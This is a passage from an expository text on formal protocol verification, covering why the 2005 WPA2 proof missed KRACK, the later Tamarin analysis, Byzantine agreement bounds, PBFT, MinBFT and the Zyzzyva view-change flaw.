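The attacker in KRACK learns only the keystream for certain counter values, never the session key, and the laptop and router are still communicating with each other. Authentication and key secrecy, the properties that He and colleagues proved, therefore hold throughout the attack. The encryption proof also remains valid, because it assumes that no counter value repeats under the same key. Neither proof covered installing the key, which resets the counter.

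Cremers, Kiesl and Medinger (2020), in *A Formal Analysis of IEEE 802.11’s WPA2*, identify three simplifications in the 2005 model, each of which would have been enough to hide KRACK:

- it did not explicitly consider the properties of the encryption;
- it included the sequence number of the group key but no other counter;
- it described each protocol as a straight line of steps, without the transitions back to earlier steps that let a device reset its counters.

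The missing transitions are a little surprising, since He and colleagues wrote that their proof holds for a variety of failure recovery strategies, and resending a lost message is a form of recovery. One of their invariants, that the number of the group key always increases, also fails outside the model, because a device can violate it and still comply with the standard.

*Modelling of 802.11 4-Way Handshake Attacks and Analysis of Security Properties* uses Tamarin to check whether attacks such as KRACK violate the properties that the standard requires of the handshake, or whether those properties are insufficient. The properties proved in 2005 were insufficient, because keeping users' data secret takes more than a secret key. The blog post *Falling through the KRACKs* (2017) makes a similar point about the 2005 proof, that in formal analysis "definitions really, really matter".

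The post also describes a worse version of the attack on Android 6, where repeating message 3 makes the device install an all-zero key. In this case the attacker does know the key, but the cause is a programming error that no proof about the standard could have ruled out.

### The repaired protocol in Tamarin

Vanhoef and Piessens argued only informally that their suggested countermeasures would work, and the standards body adopted a slightly different one. A year later, in *Release the Kraken*, Vanhoef and Piessens (2018) reported attacks that got around both the suggested and the adopted countermeasures. For example, they could still make a device reinstall a group key by combining handshake messages with sleep-mode messages. A sleeping laptop misses updates to the group key, so the router sends it the current key and counter when it wakes up. Vanhoef and Piessens concluded that formal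 modelling would help secure both the standard and its implementations.

Cremers and colleagues built such a model in Tamarin. Cremers had also worked on the TLS 1.3 proof. They had to include much more than the four messages:

- seven types of state machine, covering the two handshakes, the creation of group keys and sleep mode, with loops for repeated messages;
- a queue for outgoing messages, because a device may prepare a message before a key change and send it afterwards, encrypted with the new key;
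- the counters, both those that number handshake messages and those used in encryption.

In the model, snenc(m, k, n) is the message m encrypted with key k and counter value n. A new rule lets the attacker obtain the key if he has two different messages encrypted with the same key and counter value. This rule drops part of the assumption of perfect encryption. It is an over-approximation because it gives the attacker more than he would gain in reality.

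Cremers and colleagues could instead have proved only that a particular key is never used twice with the same counter value. But the attacker in the model would then have been unable to exploit counter reuse under any other key, and an attack might begin with such reuse.

Without countermeasures, the model allows the KRACK attacks, which is some evidence that it now contains the relevant parts of the protocol. Cremers and colleagues then added two countermeasures that Vanhoef and Piessens had proposed. A device must not change the counter of a key that is already installed, and it must delete the group key before going to sleep. With these in place, they proved four things for any number of devices and sessions:

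- the attacker learns a master key only by compromising it;
- a session key stays secret if its master key does, even if the attacker has compromised other devices on the network;
- a group key stays secret if the attacker has compromised no master key at all, a condition that is necessary because every device on the network has the group key;
- every completed handshake on one side matches exactly one run on the other, with the same keys and nonces.

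The deletion rule is meant to prevent attackers from replaying broadcasts to a device that has been asleep. Cremers and colleagues neither proved that such replays are impossible nor found one in their model. They point out that such a replay would not violate any of the properties they proved. The 2020 proof therefore has a gap similar to the one in the 2005 proof, but this time its authors identified it.

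Tamarin proved all but three of the analysis's around 70 lemmas automatically. The two authentication lemmas and one helper lemma needed some manual guidance. The whole analysis takes about two hours on an eight-core machine with 30 GB of memory, and nearly all of that time is spent on two lemmas, which state that the laptop and the router never reuse a counter value. Cremers and colleagues found that ruling out reuse was by far the hardest part of proving that the session key is secret, and earlier attempts to verify WPA2 had left this out.

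They suspect that WPA2's design discouraged other researchers from analysing it. Several of its mechanisms share nonces and counters and interact in ways that are hard to predict, whereas TLS 1.3 is relatively easy to analyse.

### From symbols to bits

Even with the extra rule, cryptography in the model is stronger than real cryptography. As in other symbolic models, nobody can guess a fresh value, and two terms are different unless an equation makes them equal.

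These assumptions leave out password guessing. The Tamarin model treats the master key as a fresh value, but on a home network the key comes from a password, which may be a common word. An attacker who records the first two handshake messages has both nonces and a checksum. He can then try passwords on his own computer, calculating the checksum for each until one matches. Cremers and colleagues note that WPA2 inherently allows this attack. Its successor, WPA3, is meant to prevent it.

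Computational soundness theorems state when a symbolic proof also holds for real cryptography. Like CryptoVerif, they assume that the attacker is a polynomial-time program that works on bits. In the general form given in *(De)Compositions of Cryptographic Schemes and their Applications to Protocols* (Janvier, Lakhnech and Mazaré, 2005), if each cryptographic scheme in a protocol meets a particular security definition, then a symbolic proof implies that the protocol is secure against this attacker. The attacker may still succeed by luck, but only with negligible probability, which means that the probability eventually falls below 1/n<sup>c</sup> for every constant c as the security parameter n grows.

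Martín Abadi and Phillip Rogaway proved the first well-known result of this type. They showed that if an attacker cannot distinguish two messages in the symbolic model, a polynomial-time program cannot distinguish the real messages either, provided the encryption meets certain conditions. Their theorem assumes an attacker who only listens, so it does not cover attacks like Lowe's or KRACK, which interfere with the exchange.

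Backes, Pfitzmann and Waidner (2008), in *Justifying a Dolev-Yao Model under Active Attacks*, extended soundness to attackers who interfere. They designed a library of cryptographic operations in two versions. The ideal version keeps a table of terms and records who has access to each, while the real version encrypts and signs strings of bits. A protocol refers to messages by local names in both, so it can use either version unchanged. They proved that the real version securely implements the ideal one, so a researcher can prove a protocol secure with the ideal version, where probability plays no part, and the result carries over to the real one. They used this method to prove Lowe's repair of the Needham-Schroeder protocol secure.

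The guarantee depends on the encryption remaining secure even if the attacker can have other encrypted messages of his choice decrypted. A weaker scheme might hide a message's contents but still let him alter them. If Z could change Bob's name to his own inside enc((N<sub>A</sub>, N<sub>B</sub>, B), K<sub>A</sub>) without opening it, Alice would accept the result and Lowe's original attack would work again. The guarantee also depends on the tags that the real library adds to encrypted messages, and on the protocol using the library's own operations to send them.

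Janvier and colleagues add the requirement that keys can be ordered so that each one encrypts only keys later in the order. This rules out cycles, such as encrypting k<sub>1</sub> with k<sub>2</sub> and k<sub>2</sub> with k<sub>1</sub>. Their theorem also covers hash functions, but only those that reveal no information about the input. Backes and colleagues report that the usual symbolic descriptions of hash functions and exclusive-or cannot be proved sound in general.

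In practice, idealising the cryptography in a proof may be a smaller problem than leaving out part of the protocol. As of 2008, Backes and colleagues knew of no protocol with a symbolic proof that had been broken when implemented with standard, provably secure cryptography, although one can construct artificial examples. A soundness theorem would not have revealed KRACK either. WPA2's encryption is secure only if no counter value repeats, so someone would still have had to check what happens to the counter when a device installs a key.

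### An unlimited attacker in a limited model

A Dolev-Yao attacker can block and repeat messages as often as he likes, but he couldn't have carried out KRACK in the 2005 model because that model had no session-key counter to reset.

The email assistant's proof could fail in the same way. Suppose the scaffold crashes after a lookup, restarts with the flag off and reloads the conversation. The model has the recovery code again, and the scaffold will now send its mail to anyone. The proof covered every request the model could make, but it had no step for a restart. Like resending message 3, restarting is an ordinary way to recover from a failure, so a designer might not see it as relevant to security.

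The 2005 proof was still useful. If its account of the four messages was accurate, an attacker could not learn the session key or impersonate the router just by manipulating those messages. Any remaining flaw had to involve something the model left out, such as how devices handle the key after receiving it. The main repair therefore leaves the four messages unchanged and only requires a device to check whether a key is already installed before resetting the counter.

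However, this only helps people who compare the proof's omissions with the assumptions of the proofs it is combined with. The encryption proof assumed that counter values never repeat, but the handshake proof did not establish this. Listing what each proof assumes and guarantees would have shown the mismatch without any new mathematics.

After Cremers and colleagues added the missing parts, symbolic analysis could detect KRACK and prove that the repair works. Their proof applies to the standard, which devices do not always follow. They cite Kr00k, a vulnerability in some Wi-Fi chips that keep encrypting and sending data after a device has disconnected. The standard does not allow this, so Kr00k does not contradict their proof, but it can still expose users of those chips.

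## The Byzantine generals: how many liars a group can tolerate

In the Byzantine problem, the network delivers every message, unlike in the Dolev-Yao model. But some participants may lie, and the rest still have to reach a common decision.

The problem arose while the research institute SRI International was developing SIFT, a fault-tolerant aircraft computer whose processors had to agree on the time, sensor readings and the results of diagnostic tests. Pease, Shostak and Lamport recall in *Reaching Agreement in the Presence of Faults* (1980) that the designers at first "naively assumed" that simple majority voting would be enough.

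Voting works if a faulty processor sends everybody the same wrong answer. But suppose processor A votes yes, B votes no, and the faulty processor C sends yes to A and no to B. A then counts two votes for yes, and B counts two for no. Sending conflicting messages to different participants is called equivocation. Pease and colleagues proved that three processors cannot tolerate one faulty one, although engineers had generally believed they could.

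### One order, two conditions

Lamport, Shostak and Pease, in *The Byzantine Generals Problem* (1982), reduce the problem to a single order. A commander sends an order, attack or retreat, to his lieutenants. Any of these generals may be a traitor, including the commander. The loyal ones follow the agreed procedure, which has to guarantee two conditions:

- *agreement*: all loyal lieutenants obey the same order;
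- *validity*: if the commander is loyal, every loyal lieutenant obeys the order he sent.

Either condition is easy to meet alone. Lieutenants who always retreat will agree, and lieutenants who always obey the commander satisfy validity. Meeting both is hard when nobody knows who the traitors are. If the commander is a traitor, no order is the right one, but the loyal lieutenants must still all do the same thing.

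A group that wants to vote can run the procedure once for each member, with that member as commander and his vote as the order. All loyal generals then have the same list of votes and reach the same result if they count it the same way.

### Why three generals are not enough

Take a commander and two lieutenants, one of the three being a traitor. The table shows two situations that Lieutenant 1 might be in.

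| Message | Lieutenant 2 is the traitor | The commander is the traitor |
|---|---|---|
| Commander to Lieutenant 1 | attack | attack |
| Commander to Lieutenant 2 | attack | retreat |
| Lieutenant 2 to Lieutenant 1 | "he told me to retreat" | "he told me to retreat" |

Lieutenant 1 never sees the middle row, so both situations look the same to him and he has to do the same thing in both. Validity requires him to attack when Lieutenant 2 is the traitor, so he must also attack when the commander is the traitor.

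But Lieutenant 2 can reason the same way. If the commander tells him to retreat and Lieutenant 1 reports an order to attack, he has to retreat, because the commander may be loyal and Lieutenant 1 may be lying. So when the commander is the traitor, Lieutenant 1 attacks and Lieutenant 2 retreats, which violates agreement.

Pease and colleagues had already proved that exchanging more messages, even an unlimited number, would not help the lieutenants find the traitor. Michael Fischer, Nancy Lynch and Michael Merritt later found a shorter proof, which Roughgarden (2021) explains in *Foundations of Blockchains*. Lamport and colleagues warn that they know of no area of computer science or mathematics in which informal reasoning is more likely to go wrong than this one.

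Suppose some protocol did work for a commander A and lieutenants B and C. We install it on six machines, two for each role, and connect them in a ring in the order A, B, C′, A′, B′, C. We then order A to attack and A′ to retreat. Each machine has one neighbour in each of the other two roles, so it can run the protocol as if it were in a group of three. We can compare each pair of neighbours with two loyal generals in a real group of three, whose traitor runs copies of the program to imitate the other four machines.

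1. A and B receive the same messages as a loyal commander who orders an attack and a loyal lieutenant. By validity, B attacks.
2. A′ and C′ receive the same messages as a loyal commander who orders a retreat and a loyal lieutenant. By validity, C′ retreats.
3. B and C′ receive the same messages as two loyal lieutenants with a traitorous commander. By agreement, they do the same thing.

These results contradict each other, so the protocol cannot exist. The proof requires only that a traitor can run the protocol. Random choices do not help, even if the generals accept a small chance of error, according to Decentralized Thoughts' *Byzantine agreement is impossible for n≤3f if the adversary can easily simulate* (2019).

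The impossibility result for three generals extends to larger groups. Suppose six generals could tolerate two traitors. Three computers could then each play two generals. If one computer were faulty, at most two of the six generals would be traitors, so the three computers would still reach agreement, which the three-general result rules out. The same argument applies to any group of n ≤ 3f generals with f traitors, because three computers can divide the roles so that each plays at most f. Tolerating f traitors therefore requires more than 3f generals.

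This limit also applies to approximate agreement. Lamport and colleagues consider generals who only have to attack within ten minutes of each other, and within ten minutes of the ordered time if the commander is loyal. If three generals could do that despite a traitor, the commander could order 1:00 to mean "attack" and 2:00 to mean "retreat". A lieutenant who settled on a time of 1:10 or earlier would attack, and one who settled on 1:50 or later would retreat. A lieutenant with a time in between would ask the other what he had decided and do the same, or retreat if the other was also undecided. Two loyal lieutenants' times would be within ten minutes of each other, so one could not choose to attack while the other chose to retreat. The three generals would then have solved the original problem, which the limit rules out.

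### Four generals and one traitor

With a fourth general, the following procedure works. Lamport and colleagues call its messages "oral" because a general who passes on an order can change it.

1. The commander sends his order to each lieutenant.
2. Each lieutenant tells the other two what he received.
3. Each lieutenant obeys the majority of his three reports, one from the commander and two from his colleagues. A missing report counts as "retreat".

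In the first case, the commander is loyal and orders an attack, but Lieutenant 3 is a traitor. Each row shows the messages that one lieutenant receives, and together the rows show nine messages.

| Recipient | From the commander | From Lieutenant 1 | From Lieutenant 2 | From Lieutenant 3 | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lieutenant 1 | attack | – | attack | retreat | attack |
| Lieutenant 2 | attack | attack | – | retreat | attack |
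| Lieutenant 3 (traitor) | attack | attack | attack | – | anything |

Lieutenant 3 can send any reports he likes, but each loyal lieutenant has two true reports against his one.

Now suppose the lieutenants are all loyal and the commander is the traitor. He tells Lieutenant 1 to attack and the other two to retreat.

| Recipient | From the commander | From Lieutenant 1 | From Lieutenant 2 | From Lieutenant 3 | Decision |
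|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Lieutenant 1 | attack | – | retreat | retreat | retreat |
| Lieutenant 2 | retreat | attack | – | retreat | retreat |
| Lieutenant 3 | retreat | attack | retreat | – | retreat |

The lieutenants pass on the orders truthfully, so each ends up with one "attack" and two "retreats". Lieutenant 1 disobeys the order he received, but all three do the same thing.

The procedure does not always reveal the traitor. In the first run, Lieutenant 1 would have received the same messages if Lieutenant 3 had been honest and the commander had told only Lieutenant 3 to retreat. Lieutenant 1 still cannot tell who is lying, but he no longer needs to, because every honest lieutenant has a majority for attack in both cases.

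### The cost of more traitors

One exchange of reports is not enough to tolerate two traitors. Suppose there are seven generals, and the commander and Lieutenant 6 are traitors. The commander tells Lieutenants 1, 2 and 3 to attack and Lieutenants 4 and 5 to retreat. Lieutenant 6 then reports "retreat" to Lieutenant 1, who has a tie and retreats by default. Lieutenant 6 also reports "attack" to Lieutenant 2, who has a majority for attack and so attacks.

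The lieutenants therefore have to agree on what Lieutenant 6 reported, which is the generals' problem again with one fewer participant. Lamport and colleagues solve it recursively. Each lieutenant passes on the order he received by acting as commander in the procedure for f − 1 traitors, with the other lieutenants as his subordinates.

The proof is by induction on f. If the commander is a traitor, at most f − 1 of the lieutenants are. There are at least 3f lieutenants, which is more than 3(f − 1), so the procedure for f − 1 traitors works and all loyal lieutenants obtain the same list of reports. If the commander is loyal, all f traitors may be lieutenants, which may be too many for that procedure to guarantee agreement. But it still delivers the loyal lieutenants' reports correctly, because loyal participants remain in the majority at every level, and these reports then outvote the traitors'.

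The number of messages rises steeply, even in the smallest groups that can tolerate f traitors:

| Traitors (f) | Generals (3f + 1) | Rounds (f + 1) | Messages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4 | 2 | 9 |
| 2 | 7 | 3 | 156 |
| 3 | 10 | 4 | 3,609 |
| 4 | 13 | 5 | 108,384 |

The problem can be solved without this explosion in messages. *Communication Lower Bounds for Cryptographic Broadcast Protocols* (2023) cites a later algorithm that finishes in f + 1 rounds with polynomial communication. Fischer and Lynch proved in 1982 that no algorithm can use fewer rounds in the worst case without some other change to the problem, such as allowing random choices. Lynch remarks in *Building a Theory of Distributed Systems* (2025) that such lower bounds are much harder to prove for ordinary sequential programs. Proofs about distributed algorithms can use the fact that each machine has only local information.

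Aspnes explains in *Notes on Theory of Distributed Systems* (2020) that the same minimum of f + 1 rounds applies even if faulty machines only crash and never lie. Tolerating lies therefore requires more machines than tolerating crashes, but not more rounds.

### What signatures change

The impossibility proof depends on the traitors' ability to misreport what others said. Suppose that every general can sign messages, that nobody can forge a loyal general's signature and that everybody can check it. Three generals can then cope with a traitorous commander:

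1. The commander signs an order to attack for Lieutenant 1 and an order to retreat for Lieutenant 2.
2. Each lieutenant forwards his signed order to the other.
3. Both lieutenants now have two conflicting orders with the commander's signature. Only he could have signed them, so they know he is the traitor.
4. Both apply the same rule to the same two orders, for example to retreat if there is more than one, and so they agree.

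If Lieutenant 2 is the traitor instead, he cannot forge the commander's signature on an order to retreat. He can only pass on the real order or stay silent, so Lieutenant 1 has one signed order and obeys it.

A traitorous commander can still sign any order in his own name, and a faulty sensor unit can still sign a false reading. But they cannot attribute a lie to someone loyal, and if they send conflicting messages to different recipients, the signed messages are evidence against them. The ring proof does not apply to signed messages because it requires the traitor to imitate loyal generals, which is impossible without their signing keys.

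With several traitors, the timing of messages matters. Suppose the commander and Lieutenant 3 are traitors. The commander sends everyone a signed order to attack, but also gives Lieutenant 3 a signed order to retreat. If Lieutenant 3 shows the retreat order to Lieutenant 1 at the last moment, Lieutenant 1 has two orders and Lieutenant 2 has only one.

To prevent this, each lieutenant who forwards an order adds his signature, and an order that arrives in round r counts only if it has r different signatures. The procedure runs for f + 1 rounds. An order that first arrives in the last round has the signatures of the commander and f lieutenants. Since the commander is a traitor in this case, at most f − 1 lieutenants are traitors. At least one of the signers is therefore loyal and has already sent the order to everybody else.

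The signed-message protocol works for any number of traitors. If 98 out of 100 generals are traitors, the two loyal ones will still do the same thing. But signatures do not reduce the number of rounds needed. *Byzantine Generals in the Permissionless Setting* (Lewis-Pye and Roughgarden, 2021) cites a 1983 proof by Danny Dolev and Ray Strong that f + 1 rounds are still necessary to tolerate f traitors.

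The limit is stricter when every general has an opinion and the group must adopt the loyal generals' opinion if they all agree. *Efficient Synchronous Byzantine Consensus* (2017) gives this limit as f < n/2. If half of the generals are traitors, they can follow the protocol while pretending to hold the opposite opinion. Signatures prove who sent each opinion, but not which half is loyal.

Signatures also raise some concerns familiar from protocol verification. The generals need each other's correct public keys in advance, as in Dolev and Yao's model. A traitor can replay an old signed order, so Lamport and colleagues recommend numbering the orders.

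### The assumptions that do the work

The guarantees rest on assumptions about the group and its communications:

- *Known membership*: every general knows who the others are. A traitor who could join under ten names would count as ten traitors.
- *Identifiable senders*: the recipient of a message knows who sent it. Lamport and colleagues suggest fixed lines between processors, because a faulty switch in a shared network could impersonate others. Signatures make this assumption unnecessary.
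- *Reliable and timely messages*: every message between loyal generals arrives unaltered, and a general can tell when an expected message is missing.
- *A cap on faults*: at most f participants are faulty. This is only plausible if faults are fairly independent, because a shared design error could affect every machine at once.

None of these assumptions predicts how a traitor will behave. Traitors may know everything, coordinate their lies, and behave perfectly for years before telling the first one. They may even share their signing keys. Signatures add only one restriction, which is that traitors cannot forge a loyal general's signature.

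The timing assumption is hard to meet. A processor can detect a missing message only if it knows how long to wait. Let μ be the longest time a message takes to prepare and deliver, and τ the largest difference between two working clocks. A processor waits for a message with k signatures until T<sub>0</sub> + k(μ + τ), where T<sub>0</sub> is the starting time. Keeping the clocks synchronised despite faulty processors is as difficult as the generals' problem.

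If there is no known limit on delays, the two-thirds requirement returns, even with signatures. Decentralized Thoughts' *On the impossibility of Byzantine agreement for n=3f in partial synchrony* (2019) presents a proof for three groups of machines. With one machine in each group, A starts with "attack", C starts with "retreat", and the faulty machine B supports "attack" in its messages to A and "retreat" in its messages to C. Messages between A and C are slow, and neither can wait indefinitely for the other, which may have crashed. A therefore decides to attack and C decides to retreat, each with B's support. They can later prove that B equivocated by comparing its signed messages, but by then they have already acted. Replicated services on ordinary networks therefore usually need more than 3f machines.

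A broken line between two processors counts as one of the f faults, because the others cannot distinguish it from a faulty processor.

Agreement also does not make a decision correct. If a faulty radar supplies bad data, the algorithm ensures only that all the working processors use the same bad data. A designer who wants a correct reading has to install several radars.

### A cracked diode on the Space Shuttle

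Byzantine faults occur in real machines without any malice. On 13 May 2008, during fuelling for the Space Shuttle mission STS-124, one of the four control computers began to disagree with the other three. Three seconds later, a second computer disagreed with all the others, and engineers had to stop the countdown. While they were looking for the cause, the remaining two computers also stopped agreeing, although all four were working correctly.

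NASA's *System Agreement Failures* traces the problem to a cracked diode in a unit that sent data to the computers over a shared line. The crack made the diode act as a capacitor, which weakened some pulses. The computers' receivers differed slightly in sensitivity, so some detected pulses that others missed. As the crack widened, the computers received increasingly different data from the same line.

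Lamport and colleagues had warned of this in 1982. Even when every processor is connected to the same wire, a faulty unit can send a marginal signal that some processors read as 0 and others as 1. They concluded that the processors have to compare what they received. In their terms, the shuttle's data unit was a traitorous commander with four loyal lieutenants. According to NASA, four computers were enough to tolerate one Byzantine fault, but the software for detecting and isolating faults did not handle such faults correctly.

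The engineer Kevin Driscoll defines a Byzantine fault as one that "presents different symptoms to different observers", a definition that does not depend on intent. In *Validation and Verification of Safety-Critical Integrated Distributed Systems* (Driscoll, 2011), he warns against systems that automatically vote out a computer that disagrees, because a single fault elsewhere can then cause the system to shut down one healthy computer after another.

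However, conflicting views do not always mean that a fault is Byzantine. In November 2020, a network switch at the internet company Cloudflare stopped forwarding some of its traffic, which cut off one machine in a three-machine cluster from the leader but not from the third machine. The switch recovered after six minutes, but the resulting database problems disrupted Cloudflare's customer dashboard for over six hours. In *A Byzantine failure in the real world*, Lianza and Snook blamed a Byzantine fault. They later added a postscript reporting that other specialists thought it was better described as an omission fault, in which messages go missing. Systems can tolerate omission faults without the overhead of Byzantine protocols.

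Lianza and Snook also defend the common decision not to use Byzantine protocols in such clusters. They argue that in many cases a simple protocol with a rare, known weakness is safer than a complex one that is hard to implement correctly. Lamport and colleagues accept that only assumptions about how machines fail can reduce the time and messages a Byzantine protocol needs, but they reject such assumptions where a system needs extremely high reliability. The case for the simple protocol is weaker if someone can prove that the complex protocol and its code are correct.

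## PBFT and the machine-checked proofs of Byzantine consensus

*Practical Byzantine Fault Tolerance* (Castro and Liskov, 1999) introduced PBFT, the protocol that much later work on Byzantine faults tries to improve. PBFT runs a service, such as a file system, on several machines called replicas, each with a full copy of the service. If the service is deterministic, copies that start in the same state and execute the same requests in the same order stay identical, so the replicas only have to agree on the order of the requests. In the paper's tests, a file system replicated with PBFT was 3% slower than a standard unreplicated one.

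The solutions to the generals' problem assumed that every message arrives within a known time. PBFT keeps the replicas consistent even if the network loses, delays, duplicates or reorders messages. The adversary may control up to f replicas and any number of clients, coordinate them, and slow down honest replicas. It cannot forge an honest replica's signature or delay messages forever. Castro and Liskov also assume that replicas fail independently, and recommend giving each one a different implementation, administrator and root password. PBFT does not guarantee secrecy, since a faulty replica can leak everything it stores.

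### Three rounds of messages

Four replicas can tolerate one faulty one. One of the four, the primary, proposes the order of requests, and the other three are backups. A client sends a signed request to the primary, and the replicas then go through three rounds:

1. *Pre-prepare*: The primary gives the request a sequence number, say 7, and sends its proposal to the backups. A backup accepts unless it has already accepted a different request for number 7 from this primary.
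2. *Prepare*: Each backup that accepts tells all the other replicas. A replica is "prepared" once it has the request, the primary's proposal and matching prepare messages from two backups, possibly including itself. Counting the primary, three replicas have then backed the same request for number 7.
3. *Commit*: Each prepared replica tells all the others that it is prepared. A replica that has three matching commit messages, including its own, executes the request as soon as it has executed numbers 1 to 6. It then sends the result to the client.

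The client accepts a result once two replicas report it, because at most one of them is faulty.

Suppose a faulty primary proposes request a to two backups and request b to the third. Three replicas can back a, but only two can back b, so no honest replica will be prepared for b. If the primary instead sends a to one backup, b to another and nothing to the third, neither request gets enough backing, and the backups eventually replace the primary.

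Without faults, the four replicas exchange 24 messages per request: 3 proposals, 9 prepare messages and 12 commit messages. For n replicas the number is 2n(n − 1), so 13 replicas exchange 312, whereas the generals' procedure without signatures needed 108,384. This comparison slightly favors PBFT, because PBFT has to repeat work under a new primary if the current one is faulty.

### Why any two quorums share an honest replica

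With n = 3f + 1 replicas, a replica cannot require messages from more than n − f = 2f + 1 of them, because the f faulty ones may stay silent. PBFT therefore uses quorums of 2f + 1. The sizes of two quorums add up to 4f + 2, but there are only 3f + 1 replicas, so they share at least f + 1. At most f of these are faulty, so at least one is honest. With four replicas, for example, two quorums of three share at least two members, at most one of which is faulty.

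The same calculation explains the number of replicas. Any two quorums of n − f replicas overlap in at least n − 2f replicas. That minimum is more than f only if n > 3f, which is the limit from the generals' problem.

Under the same primary, two honest replicas cannot be prepared for different requests with the same number. Suppose one were prepared for request a as number 7 and another for request b as number 7. A quorum would have backed each request, and at least one honest replica would belong to both quorums. That replica would have backed both requests as number 7, which honest replicas never do.

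This argument holds whatever the faulty replicas sent, even if they backed both requests, neither, or a third that nobody made. It assumes only that there are at most f faulty replicas and that they cannot forge anyone else's signature. The email assistant's proof had one case for each kind of request the model could make, but this proof needs no separate cases for the faulty replicas' behaviour.

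### Replacing the primary

If a backup waits too long for a request to complete, it stops accepting the primary's proposals and sends a view-change message to request a move to the next view. A view is a period with a single primary, and the replicas take that role in a fixed order. For every recent request for which the backup is prepared, the message includes the proposal and the matching signed prepare messages as evidence.

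The new primary collects view-change messages from a quorum, including its own. For each sequence number, it re-proposes the request whose evidence comes from the highest view, or an empty request if there is none. It also sends the backups the messages it used, so they can repeat the calculation and reject a wrong result.

The commit round is necessary because the primary can change. If replicas executed a request as soon as they were prepared, one replica might execute request a while no other replica was prepared for it. If the new primary's quorum did not include this replica, the primary would receive no evidence of a and could assign a's sequence number to another request, b, so the replicas' copies would differ.

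With the commit round, a replica executes request a only after a quorum has reported being prepared, and at least f + 1 members of that quorum are honest. Any quorum of view-change messages includes at least one of these f + 1 replicas, because f + 1 and 2f + 1 add up to more than the total of 3f + 1. That honest replica passes on the evidence for request a. Faulty replicas cannot fabricate evidence for request b from a later view, because that would require signatures from a whole quorum. Request a therefore keeps its sequence number in every later view.

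None of this depends on how long messages take, but progress does. Michael Fischer, Nancy Lynch and Michael Paterson proved in 1985 that no deterministic protocol can guarantee a decision if messages may take arbitrarily long and one machine may crash. PBFT makes progress as long as delays do not keep growing faster than its timeouts, which double after each failed view. Faulty replicas cannot stall it by constantly requesting new views, because a change requires requests from f + 1 replicas, and they cannot be primary for more than f views in a row.

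The software that Castro and Liskov measured in 1999 did not implement view changes. They argued that this did not affect the accuracy of their results, because they had formalised the complete algorithm and proved it correct. They published that proof, written by hand, as *A Correctness Proof for a Practical Byzantine-Fault-Tolerant Replication Algorithm* (1999).

### A counter that prevents equivocation

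Any two quorums must share an honest replica, because a faulty one could vote for one value in one quorum and a different value in the other. If replicas could not equivocate in this way, sharing any replica would be enough.

MinBFT, a protocol that Giuliana Veronese, Miguel Correia and colleagues published in 2013, achieves this with a small trusted component in each replica that contains a counter and a key. The component signs each message together with the next counter value and never uses a value twice. Honest replicas process each sender's messages in counter order, without skipping any values.

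Suppose a faulty primary tries to propose a to one backup and b to another. Its component signs a with value 7 and b with value 8. The backup that receives b detects that the message with value 7 is missing and does not process b until that message arrives. Both backups therefore process a first. If the primary withholds a from the second backup, that backup makes no progress with this primary and eventually requests a new one.

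MinBFT needs only 2f + 1 replicas to tolerate f faulty ones, so three replicas can tolerate one fault and five can tolerate two. Its quorums have f + 1 members. The sizes of any two quorums add up to 2f + 2, which is more than the number of replicas, so they share at least one replica. That replica may be faulty, but it cannot have sent the two quorums conflicting messages with the same number. MinBFT also needs one fewer round than PBFT. During a view change, each replica must send all the messages it has sent since the last checkpoint, so a faulty replica that omits one leaves a visible gap in the numbering.

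Ordinary signatures would not be enough, because on a slow network they may expose equivocation too late. The smaller group depends on the counter, which therefore becomes part of the trusted computing base. If an attacker could restore an old copy of the component's memory, the counter would repeat its values and the argument would fail, much as WPA2's encryption failed when the KRACK attack reset its counter.

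### How Zyzzyva lost a completed request

Zyzzyva, which won a best paper award in 2007, is a faster alternative to PBFT. Replicas execute a request as soon as the primary proposes it, and the client checks whether their answers match. If all 3f + 1 answers match, the request is complete. If only 2f + 1 match, the client combines those signed answers into a certificate and sends it to the replicas. The request is then complete once 2f + 1 replicas confirm.

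A completed request can therefore leave behind either a certificate or just matching entries in the replicas' logs. If a new primary finds both, for different requests, it prefers the certificate. Abraham, Gueta and colleagues (2017), in *Revisiting Fast Practical Byzantine Fault Tolerance*, showed that this can undo a completed request. Their example has four replicas, of which only replica 1 is faulty, and two requests that compete for the first place in the log:

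1. In view 1, replica 1 is the primary. It proposes a to replicas 2 and 3, and b to replica 4. The client of a receives answers from replicas 1, 2 and 3 and makes a certificate, which reaches only replica 1.
2. In view 2, replica 2 is the primary. It finds a in its own log and b in replica 4's. Replica 1 hides the certificate and claims to have b too. Two logs now agree on b, so replica 2 proposes b. All four replicas execute it, and b is complete.
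3. In view 3, replica 3 is the primary. It and replica 4 both report b, but replica 1 now presents the old certificate for a. Replica 3 prefers the certificate, so the replicas undo b and execute a in its place.

Every quorum had enough honest replicas, and two of them reported b. The mistake was that the new primary chose the certificate from view 1 over the log entries from view 2, whereas PBFT would have preferred the later view. Abraham and colleagues explain that this mistake is easy to miss because a certificate never conflicts with a later fast decision unless a primary equivocates. Zyzzyva's rule for choosing between two certificates, which prefers the longer log, has a similar flaw.

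They also found that an earlier protocol, FaB, can get stuck because the evidence a new primary receives may rule out every possible proposal. The FaB paper's proof that this could not happen contained a mistake.

Both flaws were found about a decade after the protocols appeared. Abraham and colleagues present them as worked scenarios and do not mention using a verification tool. Three researchers who had helped design Zyzzyva or FaB contributed to the paper. *Revisiting Fast Practical Byzantine Fault Tolerance: Thelma, Velma, and Zelma* (2018) followed with corrected designs.

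*Twins* (2020) later reproduced the Zyzzyva attack in a test. It runs two copies of a replica under one identity, which produces equivocation without anyone writing malicious code. But the testers chose the primaries and partitioned the network at each step according to the published attack, so this is not evidence that the method would have found the flaw unaided.

### Why one proof can cover any number of replicas

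Proofs about Byzantine protocols often cover every number of replicas n and faults f, whereas model checking Zyzzyva with four replicas would prove nothing about Zyzzyva with seven. Such general proofs are possible because honest replicas all run the same program, and the program usually checks only how many different replicas have sent a message, not which ones. An analysis can therefore replace the individual replicas with a few counts. This does not work for security protocols in general, because participants can create fresh values and build them into new messages, which is also what makes secrecy undecidable.

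A threshold automaton describes a protocol in terms of such counts. Take a simple broadcast in which a replica repeats a value once f + 1 replicas have sent it, and accepts the value once 2f + 1 have. Let b be the number of honest replicas that have sent it. The liars can add anything from 0 to f messages to what a replica receives, so two rules describe each step:

- an honest replica *may* repeat the value once b ≥ 1, and *must* eventually do so once b ≥ f + 1;
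- an honest replica *may* accept the value once b ≥ f + 1, and *must* eventually do so once b ≥ 2f + 1.

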